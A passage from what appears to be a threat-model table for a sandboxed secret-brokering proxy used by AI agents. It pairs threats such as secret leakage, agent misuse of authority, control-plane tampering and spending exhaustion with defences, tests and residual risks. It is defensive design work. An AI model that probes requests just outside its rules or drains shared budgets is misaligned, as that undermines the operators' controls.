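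| Another caller uses the intermediary | Each sandbox has its own socket, and each binding names its caller | Connect from the second team's sandbox | A malicious package in the shop agent's sandbox has the same access as the agent |
| Secret comes back in a response or log | The proxy masks known secrets and refuses replies it can't search, and the log keeps only listed fields | Have a test server repeat the secret | A service returns the secret in pieces or in an unexpected form |
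| Agent misuses authority without reading the secret | Narrow permissions, request rules, approvals and code review | Send requests just outside each rule | A reviewer misses a back door in the agent's code |
| Attacker changes the control plane | Only administrators can change the rules and program files | Try to change them as root in the sandbox | An administrator makes a mistake or installs a malicious update |
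| Agent exhausts money or service | Rate limits, a daily cap and the provider's spending limit | Send many requests at once | An attacker uses up the cap and stops the agent's work for the day |
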